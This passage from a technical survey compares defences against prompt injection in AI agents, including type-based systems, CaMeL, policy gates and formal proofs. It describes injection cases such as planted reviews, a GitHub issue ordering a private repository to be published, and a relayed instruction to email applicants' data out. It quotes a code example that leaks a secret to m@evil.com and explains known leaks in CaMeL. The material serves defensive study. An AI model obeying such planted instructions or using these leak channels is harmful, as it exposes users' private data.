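The one attack counted against TACIT came from a travel task. The user asked the agent to book a certain hotel, and the attacker had planted a recommendation for a rival hotel among the reviews. The agent booked the right hotel but quoted the reviews to the user word for word. AgentDojo recorded a successful attack because the rival's name appeared in the output. Odersky and colleagues argue that this broke no rule, because the policy allows public reviews to reach the user. That is a fair account of the data flow, but the user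 did receive the attacker's advertisement.

LACUNA let seven attacks through with Gemini. Zhao and colleagues acknowledge that their design doesn't stop an attacker who persuades the model to misuse a capability the task needs. The developer has to grant as little as possible, because the compiler enforces the granted scope but doesn't determine what it should be.

### Why a process sandbox misses some leaks

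A process sandbox limits which files, network addresses and system functions a running program can use. Suppose the company's sandbox lets its agent read the company folder and contact the cloud model, both of which the agent needs to do its job. A hijacked agent can read the fraud rules and include them in its next message to the model. The sandbox permits the read because the file is in an allowed folder, and it permits the connection because the address is allowed. It doesn't track how text moves from one operation to the other inside the program, so it doesn't catch the leak. Blocking either operation would stop the leak, but it would also stop the agent's legitimate work.

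TACIT tracks individual values. Reading a secret returns a wrapped string, and any function that could send the string elsewhere has a capability in its type, so such a function can't be passed to `map`. A team could get part of this protection by running two sandboxed processes, giving secrets only to one and network access only to the other, but it would then have to control everything that passes between them.

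*Safe Scala an introduction*, an article by the Scala consultancy VirtusLab, compares several kinds of sandbox. The closest to object capabilities is WebAssembly, a format for portable programs that can't reach files or the network unless their host supplies the functions for doing so. This limit applies to the whole program, but VirtusLab points out that Scala can also require a particular part of a program to be pure while another part has effects.

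Sandboxes cover things that the Scala compiler can't check, such as what an external command does once the agent's code starts it. Odersky and colleagues recommend allowing only specific commands, like `git diff` or Scala's build tool `sbt`, and adding a sandbox where security is critical. However, `sbt` runs code from a project's build files, so an agent with permission to edit those files could write ordinary Scala there and have `sbt` run it outside safe mode. The sandbox would still limit which files and network addresses that code could reach.

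## How can a whole program be checked against a policy before it runs?

If the memory function `setMemory` accepted only values whose type recorded where a refund rule came from, instead of any two strings, the compiler could reject every program that tried to store anything else. Zhou and colleagues build agents on this principle, which they call language-based agent control, and implement it in Haskell as ELBA. In Meijer's *Guardians of the Agents*, the agent instead writes out its whole plan before it reads any data, and a verifier then tries to prove that the plan obeys a policy. Both approaches prevent a program that fails the check from running.

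### Effect types

In most programming languages, a function that returns a number can also delete a file while it runs. Haskell prevents this by including effects in types. An effect type specifies how a computation may interact with the outside world. A program of type `Int` computes an integer and does nothing else, while a program of type `IO Int` may also read files, contact websites or run commands before it produces the integer.

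Zhou and colleagues give the example of a public web calculator whose agent must produce an `Int`. If a visitor asks it to delete all the files on the server and then compute the factorial of 5, the model may well write a program that does both. But the deletion command has an `IO` type, which gives the whole program an `IO` type, so the typechecker rejects it.

ELBA adds one function, `agent`, to Haskell. The developer gives it a prompt and a set of definitions that the agent may use, and the code around the call determines the type of the result. ELBA asks the model for a program and checks the program against that type. If the check fails, the model gets the error and can try again, as in TACIT.

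The bibliography agent, whose files should contain only records from DBLP, uses a small library. In outline, its functions have these types:

```haskell
dblpSearch      :: String -> BibIO [DOI]
dblpFetchBib    :: DOI -> BibIO (Trusted Bib)
appendToBibFile :: FilePath -> Trusted Bib -> BibIO ()
```

A `DOI` identifies a paper, and `BibIO` is an effect type that the developer defined for this library. The agent's program must have the type `BibIO ()`, where `()` means it returns no value. Haskell's ordinary file-writing function has an `IO` type, so the program can't run it. The constructor of `Trusted` is hidden inside the library, like the private fields of `AdmittedWrite`, so the agent can get a `Trusted Bib` only by fetching a record from DBLP. The agent can still sort and filter records with ordinary code.

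The types establish only where an entry came from, so an agent could still fetch a genuine paper on the wrong subject and add it to the file. Zhou and colleagues tested the library on 100 requests for computer science bibliographies, counting a citation as hallucinated if its authors, year or DOI were wrong. ELBA produced no hallucinated citations out of 925, while an ordinary agent with a web search tool produced 19 out of 1,002. The ordinary agent typed its citations from search results and memory, so much of the difference probably comes from copying records directly from a database. A tool that fetched and stored each entry in one step should do as well on this measure.

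The model writes an ELBA program before the program runs, so the model can't react to the results. To let a model respond to them, the program can call `agent` again and include the results in the new prompt. For example, the bibliography agent might search for "differential privacy", fetch the first result and pass it to a second agent, which decides whether to refine the search or write to the file. The second call appears inside a `BibIO` program, so Haskell infers the type `BibIO ()` for it, and the second agent can't write ordinary files either. The first agent can give the second a narrower type, such as one that allows no effects, but not `IO`.

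### Paths, labels and the timing of each check

ELBA's file library uses capabilities. The developer chooses a root directory, and the agent's program receives a value of type `Path` for it. The file functions accept only a `Path`, so a program that passes the string `"/etc/passwd"` doesn't compile. The operator `//` narrows a path, as in `root // "input.txt"`. The expression `root // "../../etc/passwd"` compiles because both operands have the right type, but `//` rejects it at run time. An agent can also pass a narrower `Path` to another agent, for example to give each subagent one customer's folder.

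For information-flow control, ELBA uses LIO, an existing Haskell library. LIO labels data with who may see it and which sources influenced it. Each computation also has a current label, which changes as the computation reads data. If a program fetches a page from phony.com, its current label records that site's influence. If the program then tries to write to a channel that requires the user's own authority, LIO stops it with an error. This blocks correct rules too, as does judging a refund rule by the least trusted text the agent has read.

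LIO's `toLabeled` function avoids that problem by running part of a program separately and returning the result in a sealed, labeled wrapper, which leaves the main program's label unchanged. One agent can read an untrusted message and draft a reply inside `toLabeled`, and the main agent can pass the sealed draft to a sending function that checks the draft's label. The main agent's label changes if it opens the draft. This resembles the dual-LLM pattern that the programmer Simon Willison proposed, in which one model has tools but never sees untrusted data, and another reads the untrusted data but has no tools. In ELBA, the agent that reads the untrusted message can keep its tools, because LIO checks each call against the current label.

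| Condition | When ELBA checks it |
|---|---|
| The program uses only permitted kinds of effect | Before the program runs |
| A bibliography entry has the type `Trusted Bib` | Before the program runs |
| A file function receives a `Path` | Before the program runs |
| The `Path` lies inside the permitted directory | While the program runs |
| The current label permits this write | While the program runs |

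A type error requires only another request to the model, because no tool has run yet. An LIO error can occur partway through a program, after earlier actions have taken effect, and ELBA doesn't retry after such an error.

### Why the application needs the same language

Zhou and colleagues prove that extending a typed language with `agent` preserves every property that its type system guarantees. A type-system property is a condition on traces that every well-typed program of a certain type satisfies, where a trace is the sequence of externally visible tool calls in one run. For programs of type `BibIO ()`, one such property is that every entry written to disk came from DBLP.

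The proof replaces each call to `agent` with an ordinary function that queries the model, typechecks the reply and runs it. The new program has the same type and traces as the old one, but it belongs to the original language, so the original guarantee applies to it. A generated program may itself call `agent`, so each call has a limit on how deeply such calls can nest, and the proof is by induction on that limit. The proof makes no assumption about which programs the model writes, so it also covers a hijacked model. However, it adds no new guarantees, so if `appendToBibFile` had a flaw that let false entries through, an agent calling it could add them too.

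The theorem applies to the whole program that contains the agents, including the code that passes results between them and retries after failures. If a Python application requested Haskell snippets, ran them and saved their results with Python's own file functions, the types would cover the snippets but not the Python code that saved the results.

Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026), in *The LLMbda Calculus*, found a weakness of this kind in CaMeL. Its interpreter tracks secrets, but an ordinary Python loop outside the interpreter retries programs that fail. Whether a policy blocks an attempt can depend on a secret, so each attempt can reveal one bit of it, and repeated attempts can reveal all of it. In ELBA's experiments, the theorem likewise didn't cover AgentDojo's tools, because they are written in Python and ELBA reached them through another process.

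### Tests with hijacked subagents

Zhou and colleagues compared ELBA with CaMeL on AgentDojo's Slack tasks. There are 21 user tasks and 5 injected tasks, which gives 105 pairs. They ran four models on every pair with three different styles of attack, and switched each system's policies on and off. No injection succeeded against either system, even without policies. The standard attacks therefore provide no evidence that the policies improved security, though they do show what the policies cost:

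| Tasks completed, range over four models | ELBA | CaMeL |
|---|---|---|
| With policies, no attack (of 21) | 8–10 | 4–6 |
| With policies, under attack (of 105) | 40–52 | 22–30 |
| Without policies, no attack (of 21) | 14–18 | 13–17 |
| Without policies, under attack (of 105) | 78–93 | 55–84 |

With policies on, ELBA completed roughly twice as many tasks as CaMeL. Under the attack style that AgentDojo calls direct, the 95% confidence interval for the difference was above zero for all four models. Without policies, the gap was smaller, and GPT 5.4 did slightly better with CaMeL in three of the four conditions. The two systems also enforce different policies, which may explain some of ELBA's advantage. ELBA lowers an agent's privileges to those of any source it reads. ELBA took about three times as long as CaMeL, mainly because its agents call the model again whenever they need to respond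 to data.

Since the standard attacks all failed, Zhou and colleagues simulated a worse one. ELBA's agents read all outside data through recursive calls, whose prompts contain a task and some input. The researchers changed ELBA so that whenever the input contained the marker "TODO:", which AgentDojo's direct attacks use, the subagent received only the input, and the attacker's text became its entire prompt. They ran the 105 pairs seven times per model with policies and seven times without, for 735 runs per model in each condition.

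| Model | Resisted, with policies | Completed, with policies | Resisted, without | Completed, without |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Opus 4.7 | 735 | 351 | 425 | 523 |
| Claude Opus 4.8 | 735 | 312 | 460 | 557 |
| GPT 5.4 | 735 | 338 | 621 | 558 |
| Claude Sonnet 5 | 735 | 294 | 540 | 494 |

The policies did help in this test. Without them, between 16% and 42% of injections succeeded, depending on the model. The models therefore resisted most injections on their own, although Zhou and colleagues describe the test as forcing subagents to carry out the attacker's instructions. The perfect scores also depend partly on Zhou and colleagues' own judgement. AgentDojo flagged 29 of the 2,940 runs as successful attacks because the agent had opened a certain web address. They reviewed all 29 and found no violation, since opening the address leaked nothing.

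The policies also forbid some legitimate behaviour, so they reduced the share of user tasks completed from 67–76% to 40–48%. Zhou and colleagues suggest that a system could still use such a policy as a filter, running whatever the policy allows and asking a person only about the rest.

### Plans with preconditions and postconditions

Meijer's article, first published in 2025 and reprinted in January 2026, compares prompt injection to SQL injection and proposes the same remedy, separating code from data. When asked to summarize a user's emails, the model writes a three-step JSON plan to fetch the emails, summarize them and return the summary. The plan refers to the emails by the name `emails_fetched` because they haven't been fetched yet. An instruction hidden in one of the emails arrives after the plan is complete, so it can't add a step.

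A bad step can still enter the plan earlier. The email tool's description might contain a claim that compliance rules require sending a copy of every summary to an outside address, or the user might ask for such a copy. The verifier therefore checks the plan before it runs. One of Meijer's rules forbids any flow from the fetched emails (the source) to the body of an outgoing email (the sink) unless the recipient is in the company's own domain. Existing tools for analysing source code can search a plan for such a flow.

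Other policies concern what a step does. They use preconditions, which must hold before a step runs, and postconditions, which must hold afterwards. The verifier assumes that each tool meets its postconditions and tries to prove that the whole plan has the required result.

Suppose the user asks the agent to delete `foo.txt` and `bar.txt`, and the agent plans the single call `delete_file("*.txt")`, which deletes every text file. Let F be the set of files before the plan runs and F′ the set afterwards. A first attempt at the conditions might be:

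```text
delete_file(pattern):  F′ contains no file that matches pattern
the whole plan:        F′ contains neither foo.txt nor bar.txt
```

The bad plan passes. If no text files remain, then `foo.txt` and `bar.txt` are certainly gone. The conditions lack a frame condition, which requires everything else to stay as it was. With one on each line, they become equations:

```text
delete_file(pattern):  F′ = F without the files that match pattern
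the whole plan:        F′ = F without foo.txt and bar.txt
```

Now the verifier rejects the bad plan, because F might contain `notes.txt`, which the call would also delete. It accepts a plan that deletes the two files one by one. Both the requirement on the whole plan and `delete_file` need a frame condition. Without the one on `delete_file`, the verifier couldn't rule out that deleting `foo.txt` removes other files too, and it would reject the good plan. In the published version, Meijer adds a frame condition only to `delete_file` and claims that the bad plan then fails, but that plan would still satisfy the original requirement that the two files be gone.

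Nada Amin and others have built an open-source verifier, also called Guardians, from the article. According to *Background And Related Work* in the documentation of clauz3, a similar tool for Python programs, Guardians checks conditions like these with Z3, which solves logical formulas automatically. It also has rules for sources and sinks, and security automata, which restrict the order of tool calls. clauz3's *Guardians Synergies* gives the example of requiring approval before any transfer of money.

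In Guardians, an operator writes the policy, and agents can't weaken it. In clauz3, the agent proposes a contract together with its program, for example that the program will email only Bob, and at most once. The tool proves that the program keeps the contract, and the user decides whether to accept the contract. This suits one-off tasks for which nobody has written a policy, but the user has to notice when a contract allows too much.

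In a 2026 talk, summarized in AI Engineer's *Make the Agent Produce a Program Before It Can Act* (2026), Meijer has the agent supply the proof as well as the program. The idea comes from proof-carrying code, a 1990s technique in which an untrusted party delivers a program with a proof of its safety, and a small trusted checker verifies the proof before the program runs. The summary gives an example in Lean, a language for programs and proofs. An agent plans to read a file and report its length, and proves that the plan never deletes anything, whatever the file contains. The proof doesn't cover confidentiality, and it would be worthless if the software that runs the plan secretly deleted files while reading them.

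Meijer reports no experiments. He acknowledges that nobody has formally measured how planning everything in advance affects an agent's performance, though he expects it to help.

### A rule about private repositories

Conditions can also be part of ordinary types. In *AeonBox*, Fonseca describes an agent that can act only through a GitHub library written in aeon, a research language with liquid types. A liquid type attaches a logical condition to a type, and a solver checks the condition automatically. For example, a division function can require that its second argument not be zero. A program that divides by a number read from the user then compiles only if it first makes sure the number isn't zero. Similarly, an invoice tool could require an amount of at most $50,000, and the compiler would reject any program that approves an invoice without first checking that the amount is within the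 limit.

AeonBox uses liquid types to stop an agent from publishing private code. The library passes around a session object whose type records whether the agent has read a private repository, in which case the session is tainted. Simplified, the two main rules are:

```text
repoRead(s, r)     returns a session s2 with
                   tainted(s2) = private(r) or tainted(s)

createIssue(s, r)  requires tainted(s) = false
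                   and private(r) = false
```

In Fonseca's example, a user asks for the most urgent issue in a project. The latest issue contains an instruction to publish the contents of the largest private repository, and the agent writes a program to do so. The program would read the repository, which returns a session with `tainted(s2) = true`, and then use that session to create a public issue. `createIssue` requires a session for which `tainted` is `false`, so the program doesn't compile and never reads the private repository.

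The program could avoid the rule by keeping the original, untainted session and using it to post the issue. AeonBox prevents this by making sessions linear. A linear value is like an affine one, except that a program must use it exactly once, so reading a repository uses up the old session. An agent could also escape the rule if it could call the library function that creates untainted sessions, so Fonseca has the surrounding software create them. That software also keeps track of the session between programs. Otherwise, the model could read private code in one program and paste it into a public issue in another.

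The rule applies to the session, not to particular data, so after reading a private repository the agent can't create any public issue, even a harmless one. Fonseca illustrates AeonBox with this one attack and reports no benchmark results.

### What the LLMbda calculus proves

Systems that track data flow are easy to get wrong. Garby and colleagues found a second leak in CaMeL, based on an example that J. S. Fenton published in 1974. Adapted to a bank balance that should stay secret, it looks like this:

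```python
rich = True
tmp = True
if balance > threshold:
    tmp = False
if tmp:
    rich = False
if rich:
    send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

If the balance is high, the program sets `tmp` to false, and CaMeL marks `tmp` as secret. The next branch doesn't run, so `rich` stays true and keeps its public label, and CaMeL allows the email. If the balance is low, `rich` becomes false and no email goes out. The attacker can learn which case holds because CaMeL marks only the variables that a program actually changes.

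Garby and colleagues designed LLMbda, a small formal language, to prove the absence of such leaks. It extends the lambda calculus, a minimal language of functions that researchers use to study programming languages. LLMbda programs can prompt a language model, run code that the model writes, and copy or clear the conversation. Every value has a label that marks it as secret, untrusted, both or neither, and a result inherits the labels of everything that influenced it. The conversation also has a label, so once it contains an untrusted email, any code the model then writes counts as untrusted, and a payment tool can refuse that code's requests.

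The property they prove is a form of noninterference, which means that changing the secrets doesn't change what an outsider can observe. A language model's replies are random, so the definition compares probabilities. Let μ₀(q) and μ₁(q) be the probabilities that an outsider sees the result q when the secret has one value or another. They may add up to less than 1, because a run may never finish or a policy check may stop it. The definition requires a third set of probabilities ω, with a total of at most 1, such that

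ω(q) ≥ μ₀(q) and ω(q) ≥ μ₁(q) for every result q.

Suppose an agent always answers "yes" when the balance is high and "no" when it is low. Then ω would have to be 1 for both answers, a total of 2, so the definition forbids this program. Suppose instead that with a high balance the agent answers "yes" half the time and otherwise never finishes, while with a low balance it answers "yes" or "no" with equal probability. Setting ω to one half for each answer works, so the definition permits this program. It still leaks a little, because an outsider who sees "no" learns that the balance is low. Garby and colleagues prove that the distance between the two distributions of answers is at most the average probability of not finishing, which here is (0.5 + 0) / 2 = 0.25. If a permitted program always finishes, the two distributions must be identical.

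Their first theorem is that every LLMbda program has this property, including agents that generate and run code. This is stronger than the theorem about ELBA, which transfers whatever guarantees the host language already has. Lean has also checked the LLMbda proofs. Another theorem shows that the interpreter, which runs real agents, produces results with the probabilities the theory assigns to them, provided the model's replies follow the assumed distribution.

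Strict tracking would make some ordinary tasks impossible, so LLMbda has an operation called `endorse` that marks an untrusted value as trusted. For example, an agent may need to use the category of a customer's email as the subject of its reply. If the program accepts only eight categories, an attacker who controls the email can choose among eight subjects (three bits of influence) but can't write a new one. The second main theorem is that `endorse` can't release secrets, however a program uses it. The theorem doesn't limit how much untrusted data a program can endorse, so a careless program can endorse any amount.

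In the theorems, tools and data sources are part of the LLMbda program, and Garby and colleagues acknowledge that a better model would include real external tools. Developers also have to label each source correctly and put a check before every sensitive action.

### Fixed plans and programs that take turns

Meijer's agent completes its plan before it reads any data. ELBA and AeonBox let an agent keep writing code after it has read data, so hostile text can influence the later code. Garby and colleagues' experiments give some idea of how much protection comes from fixing the plan in advance and how much from checking it.

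Garby and colleagues wrote an agent in LLMbda called Randori, which practises on made-up data until its plan works and then runs the plan on the real data. They tested it on AgentDojo's banking tasks, where 16 user tasks and 9 injections make 144 pairs. In 97 pairs, the attack needs an action that a sensible plan for the user's task would never include, such as a payment when the user asked for a summary of recent transactions. Fixing the plan in advance is generally enough to stop these attacks. In the other 47, the plan already contains an action that the attacker could redirect, for example by changing the account number in a bill, so the agent has to track where its data came from. Garby and colleagues argue that in systems like ELBA and TACIT, stopping the attack would depend on the types in all 144 pairs.

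A fixed plan can also let the data determine which actions the agent takes. In one banking task, the agent is told to read a file and follow its instructions precisely. With CaMeL's policies switched off, the model wrote a plan with a loop that read each instruction and called the matching tool. The plan never changed, but whoever wrote the file could choose the actions, and two attacks succeeded this way.

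Fixed plans work less well when the next step depends on what the agent finds. Zhou and colleagues attribute CaMeL's lower scores on the Slack tasks to this, but Randori's results suggest that strict policies also contribute. Without attacks, Randori completed between 31 and 36 of 48 attempts, depending on the model. With the two models that Garby and colleagues tried, CaMeL completed 32 and 34 when its policies were off, and 18 when they were on. Randori also plans in advance, but its plans can endorse particular values. Removing `endorse` lowered its score from 36 to 30 with one model and from 31 to 26 with another.

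Across three models and three repetitions of the 144 pairs, Randori resisted all but 2 of 1,296 attacks. Both successful attacks involved the same pair, in which the user asks the agent to pay a bill by following the instructions in a text file, and the attacker replaces the file's contents with a different payment request. The plan endorsed the file's contents because the task required it. Removing `endorse` blocks the attack but also blocks the payment the user wanted, since the file has the same label whether it contains the real bill or the attacker's.

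## Would one central runtime checkpoint do as well?

Typed admission protects the company's memory only from code that the compiler checks. A Python script with the database password can still store a false refund rule. The strongest alternative is to put the check inside the only component that can carry out the action. Suppose a separate memory service has the only password to the database and checks every write it receives. The developer's import routine, the Python script and the agent can all send it requests, but none can write to the database directly, so none can skip the check.

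This is the reference monitor that Anderson's panel recommended in 1972. It differs from the hooks in agent frameworks because the check is part of the operation. *Agent libOS* (Zhang, 2026) describes a runtime for agents that acquire new tools as they work, and argues that a confirmation step is insufficient if it sits in a wrapper around the operation that touches the resource, because a new tool could use the same operation without the wrapper. *SecureClaw* (Ma and Schmid, 2026) adds that some tools with real effects take no arguments, so a filter on arguments has nothing to examine.

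### How CaMeL checks a tool call

*Defeating Prompt Injections by Design*, a 2025 paper by Debenedetti and colleagues at Google DeepMind, introduced CaMeL, which extends Willison's dual-LLM pattern. In *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks* (April 2025), Willison welcomed it as an exception to more than two years of little progress against prompt injection.

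Suppose a user asks an agent to confirm a refund to the customer who sent the latest support email. With simplified function names, CaMeL's plan might be:

```python
mail = read_latest_email("support")
address = ask_reader("Find the customer's address.", mail, EmailAddress)
send_email(address, "Your refund is on its way.")
```

Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues (2026), in *CaMeLoT*, describe how the system handles such a plan:

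1. A planning model reads the user's request and writes the program, in a restricted form of Python. It never reads the email.
2. CaMeL's interpreter runs the first line and attaches two labels to `mail`. One records the text's sources, and the other records who may read it.
3. The interpreter gives the email to another model, which has no tools and returns only a value. The interpreter stores that value as `address`, with labels of its own.
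4. Before sending anything, the interpreter calls a policy function. This ordinary Python function receives the tool's name, its arguments and their labels, and returns "allow" or "deny" with a reason. The interpreter calls the email tool only if the answer is "allow".

As in Meijer's design, an instruction hidden in the email can't add a step to the plan, because the plan is fixed before the email is read. The instruction can make the second model return the attacker's address, but a policy that refuses recipients from untrusted sources will stop the message. That policy also refuses the customer's real address, since it came from the email too.

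The label for readers lets a policy forbid emailing private data to anyone who isn't allowed to read it. For a calendar event, the permitted readers might be the user and the people invited. CaMeL's documentation calls these labels capabilities, but they describe data and don't give their holder permission to do anything.

The guarantee depends on the interpreter labelling everything correctly. Besides the leaks through untaken branches and retries, Garby and colleagues found that an untrusted value became trusted when it was inserted into a string literal. For example, an attacker's address could lose its "untrusted" label when the program put it into a sentence.

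### What CaMeL costs in completed tasks

The first version of the CaMeL paper, from March 2025, reported that CaMeL solved 67% of AgentDojo's tasks. The June 2025 version reported 77%, compared with 84% for an undefended agent. According to Garby and colleagues, two injections succeeded in that evaluation. In one, the user had asked the agent to make a payment as a document instructed, a case the CaMeL paper places outside its threat model. The other was the hotel review that AgentDojo also counted against TACIT.

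Other groups later measured lower completion rates. Turning on the policies roughly halved the number of completed tasks in Garby and colleagues' banking tests, and reduced it by more than half in Zhou and colleagues' Slack tests. Nikolaou and colleagues tested CaMeL with Claude Haiku 4.5, and it completed 49 of AgentDojo's 97 tasks. They ran no attacks, yet both CaMeL and their own checker blocked 17 of the tasks. These results aren't directly comparable, because the groups used different models and set-ups.

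Policies are only part of the reason agents complete fewer tasks with CaMeL. In *Can CaMeLs Talk?*, Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues (2026) tested five models without policies on AssetOpsBench, where one agent delegates professional tasks to four specialists. Adding CaMeL to every agent reduced the completion rate by an average of 21.6 percentage points. For the two strongest models, Claude Fable 5 and GPT-5.5, the average drop was 13.4 points. The planning model has to write code that handles a tool's result before seeing that result, so the researchers gave it a description of each result's format. Without those descriptions, CaMeL would probably have done worse.

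Running time and token use also increase. *ToolFence* (2026) reports that CaMeL was significantly slower than defences based on prompts or filters, because its programs are longer than ordinary tool calls. *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (2026) applies a similar design to agents that operate a computer, and reports a token overhead of 1.88 times relative to an undefended agent.

### When one agent instructs another

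A company with several agents may have a checkpoint in each one. Peters-Gill and colleagues showed that this setup can fail even if every checkpoint works as designed. They built a system with a coordinating agent, a database agent and a notification agent, all running CaMeL. A user asked it to send Julie a Slack message summarizing the job applicants. The database contained a planted instruction to email the applicants' details to an outside address.

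The database agent and the coordinator both handled the planted text as data. The coordinator then put its summary into the sentence it sent to the notification agent. That agent's planning model treated the sentence as a request from its user and wrote a plan that messaged Julie and also emailed the attacker.

The experiment used no policies, but a policy on untrusted recipients might not have helped. The attacker's address reached the notification agent inside an instruction that the agent treated as trusted, so its interpreter had no basis for labelling the address as untrusted.

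Peters-Gill and colleagues prove that the problem is general to systems where agents call other agents as tools. If any tool returns untrusted data, some user request will lead one agent to include that data in an instruction to another. The proof assumes only that the agents can make ordinary plans, such as calling a tool and using its result in the next call.

The proposed remedy, multi-CaMeL, gives each call between agents two arguments. One holds the instruction, which the interpreter rejects if it depends on any tool's output. The other holds data, which the receiving agent's program can use but its planning model can't read. The labels travel with the data, so policies can apply across all the agents.

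Peters-Gill and colleagues tested this on a version of AgentDojo that divides the tools among several agents, with 949 attack trials per model in each condition. Averaged over five models, attacks succeeded in 12.9% of trials without CaMeL, in 0.2% with a separate CaMeL in each agent, and in none with multi-CaMeL. On AssetOpsBench, the change reduced the share of tasks completed by another 3.2 percentage points on average. GPT-5.5 resisted every attack even without a defence, so its results can't show whether either design helped. They warn that stronger attacks might still succeed against it.

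### Faramesh's standard form

Fatmi's Faramesh checks each action just before execution and leaves the agent's plan alone. It first rewrites the action in a standard form. For example, two requests to send the same email may list the recipient and subject in a different order, and one may include an empty field. Faramesh converts both to the same sequence of bytes, then computes a hash from it.

The policy gate then evaluates the standard form together with the current policy and a fingerprint of the system's state. It permits the action, denies it or defers it to a person, and records the decision. The executor runs an action only if it receives a signed approval for that action's hash. If the gate is unavailable or times out, nothing runs.

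The standard form prevents an agent from getting a different answer by rewording a request. This works well for calls with fixed fields, the kind Fatmi tested. Fatmi claims more broadly that actions with the same meaning have the same standard form. No program can ensure this for arbitrary code or shell commands, because it is impossible in general to decide whether two programs always do the same thing.

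Faramesh also uses the hash to prevent duplicates. In one test, 64 concurrent workers submitted the same request a million times, and it never ran twice. But if a company owes a supplier the same amount two months in a row, Faramesh could treat the second payment request as a repeat of the first unless something distinguishes it, such as an invoice number.

Fatmi ran these tests on a single Apple M1 computer. Half the decisions took less than 2.24 milliseconds and 95% took less than 9.61. All 10,000 direct calls to the executor without an approval failed. However, Fatmi gives a coverage score of 0.9993 for normal operation, which by Fatmi's formula means that 7 in 10,000 attempts executed without a valid approval. Fatmi attributes the gap to faults and malformed requests that the test program introduced on purpose, but an execution boundary should have stopped those too.

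Ma and Schmid tested Faramesh with GPT-4o mini and compared it with an undefended agent:

| Measure | Undefended | Faramesh |
|---|---|---|
| Successful attacks, AgentDojo | 31.48% | 22.89% |
| Legitimate tasks completed, AgentDojo | 70.10% | 60.82% |
| Successful attacks, Agent Security Bench | 91.65% | 0.00% |
| Tasks completed under attack, Agent Security Bench | 0.85% | 3.70% |
| Trials with a leak, AgentLeak | 93.95% | 93.95% |

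The executor can enforce a decision perfectly and still run a harmful action that the policy allows, so these results depend heavily on the policy used in the test. Ma and Schmid also developed a competing system. The AgentLeak result is easier to explain, because the benchmark includes secrets that agents pass to one another or write to shared memory, and a check on outgoing actions doesn't control what an agent has already read.

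### A commercial policy engine

Amazon offers a central checkpoint as part of Bedrock AgentCore, its platform for running agents. AgentCore Policy applies rules at a gateway between agents and their tools. Developers write the rules in Cedar, which Symbiont also uses. A rule for the purchasing agent with the $50,000 limit could look like this:

```cedar
permit (
  principal == Agent::"purchasing",
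  action == Action::"approve_invoice",
  resource
)
when { context.amount <= 50000 };
```

The `principal` is whoever makes the request, and `context` holds further facts, such as the invoice amount. Cedar denies a request unless a `permit` rule matches it, and a matching `forbid` rule overrides every `permit`. If this were the only rule, the gateway would refuse the $1,200,000 invoice without anyone writing a rule against it.

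Cedar evaluates the facts it receives and doesn't trace where they came from. A rule could refuse a memory write whose source is a customer's email, but some trusted component would have to supply the source. The gateway also can't check a call that bypasses it. If the agent's process holds a password for the invoice system, it can approve the large invoice directly.

### The Command Gate and its theorem

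Bhattarai and Vu (2026), in *Trustworthy Agentic AI Requires Deterministic Architectural Boundaries*, propose a gate that accepts only a fixed list of action types. Their example for a research assistant includes retrieving documents, summarizing them, writing to memory and sending email. The design has three steps:

1. The model proposes an action by choosing a type from the list and filling in its parameters.
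2. A policy checker that uses no language model evaluates a function σ, which takes the action, its parameters and the context and returns "allow" or "deny". The context includes the user's identity and the labels on the data.
3. If σ returns "allow", a trusted adapter translates the action into a real tool call.

The list is finite, but it covers infinitely many possible actions. A memory write has a text parameter, so writing the false refund rule to memory is a well-formed action, and σ has to reject it. One of the sample policies would reject it because it by default denies writes to memory shared between users.

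Another sample policy restricts access to confidential files if the agent's most recent input was untrusted. As worded, it might fail if the agent read a hostile web page and then a harmless internal document, because the most recent input would then be trusted.

According to the Command Gate theorem, no model output can cause an action to execute if the action is missing from the list or σ denies it. The theorem assumes that σ is deterministic and uses no language model, and that every action passes through the gate (complete mediation). Since the gate executes only listed actions that σ allows, no other action can execute.

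The theorem is correct, but its proof depends almost entirely on assuming complete mediation, the property that is hardest to achieve in a real system. The theorem also doesn't show whether σ allows the right actions. Bhattarai and Vu report no measurements. Their figures, such as a median authorization time below 50 milliseconds, are targets for future tests.

For the company's memory, an engineer would have to establish complete mediation by closing the other routes to the database:

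- Give the database password only to the memory service, and change it, because copies of the old one may remain in configuration files and backups.
- Configure the network so that the database accepts connections only from that service.
- Remove any general shell or file tool that could reach the database's storage.
- Make imports, migrations and restored backups use the service too, or review those programs as carefully as the service itself.

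The engineer should then try to write to the database from the agent's machine, first with the old password and then with the new one. Both attempts should fail. This test covers only the routes that somebody thought of, and a later change to the network can open another one.

A careful design can also contain exceptions. Zhang requires every operation to pass admission before it reaches an outside service or the file system, but allows one check of a Git repository before admission. The check is read-only and returns limited information. Zhang documents the exception, so a reviewer can examine it.

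### Four designs compared

The comparison assumes that someone has set up each design as intended:

| Design | Who can omit the check | When people discover an omission | Facts the rule can use | Existing code that must change |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Caller-invoked guardrail | Any developer who calls the operation, or an agent that writes its own code | During code review, or after a harmful action | Any run-time fact the caller supplies or the check can look up | Each calling place, or the framework's settings |
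| Central checkpoint | Anyone with another route to the resource | During an audit of access, or after an incident | Arguments, identity, current records, approvals and any labels the system tracks | Tools move behind the checkpoint, and operators change credentials and network rules |
| Typed admission | Code inside the trusted module, or code that reaches the resource by another route | At compile time if code calls the typed operation, otherwise as with a guardrail | Any run-time fact in the admission function; the types record that the function approved the action | The operation's signature and every caller |
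| Capability-safe agent code | The author of a library function that lacks the check; the agent's code can't reach the resource without a capability | Before the agent's code runs if it lacks a capability, otherwise during a review of the library | The types show which capabilities code can use; library functions can check run-time facts | Tools become a typed library, and operators disable the agent's other tools |

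A central checkpoint works better than typed admission when a company has programs in several languages. The memory service handles requests from Python and Rust the same way, and the programmers don't have to learn a new type. Some old code still has to change, because scripts that open the database directly will stop working.

If the developer of the import routine forgets to call the evaluation function, the memory service still evaluates the rules. But if the routine tries to open the database itself, it fails only when it runs, perhaps overnight. Typed admission catches a forgotten evaluation earlier, at compile time.

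### Facts that exist only at run time

Many rules depend on facts that aren't available at compile time. Nikolaou and colleagues tried to check CaMeL's 28 AgentDojo policies against a plan before running it, and could do so for 22. The other six depend on run-time state, such as who can read a shared file when an agent uses it.

In Zhang's design, an operation can run only if the agent's process is still active and holds the necessary capability. The operation must also fall within the limits of the current task, satisfy the policy or have a person's approval, and fit the remaining budget. The design requires checking these conditions again when the operation runs, because the facts may have changed since an earlier preview.

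An `AdmittedWrite` stays valid even if Alice, who approved it, has since left the company, so only a check at the time of the write can catch her departure. A late check also leaves less time for the facts to change before the write, but they can still change unless the database runs the check and the write as one transaction.

### What types can add

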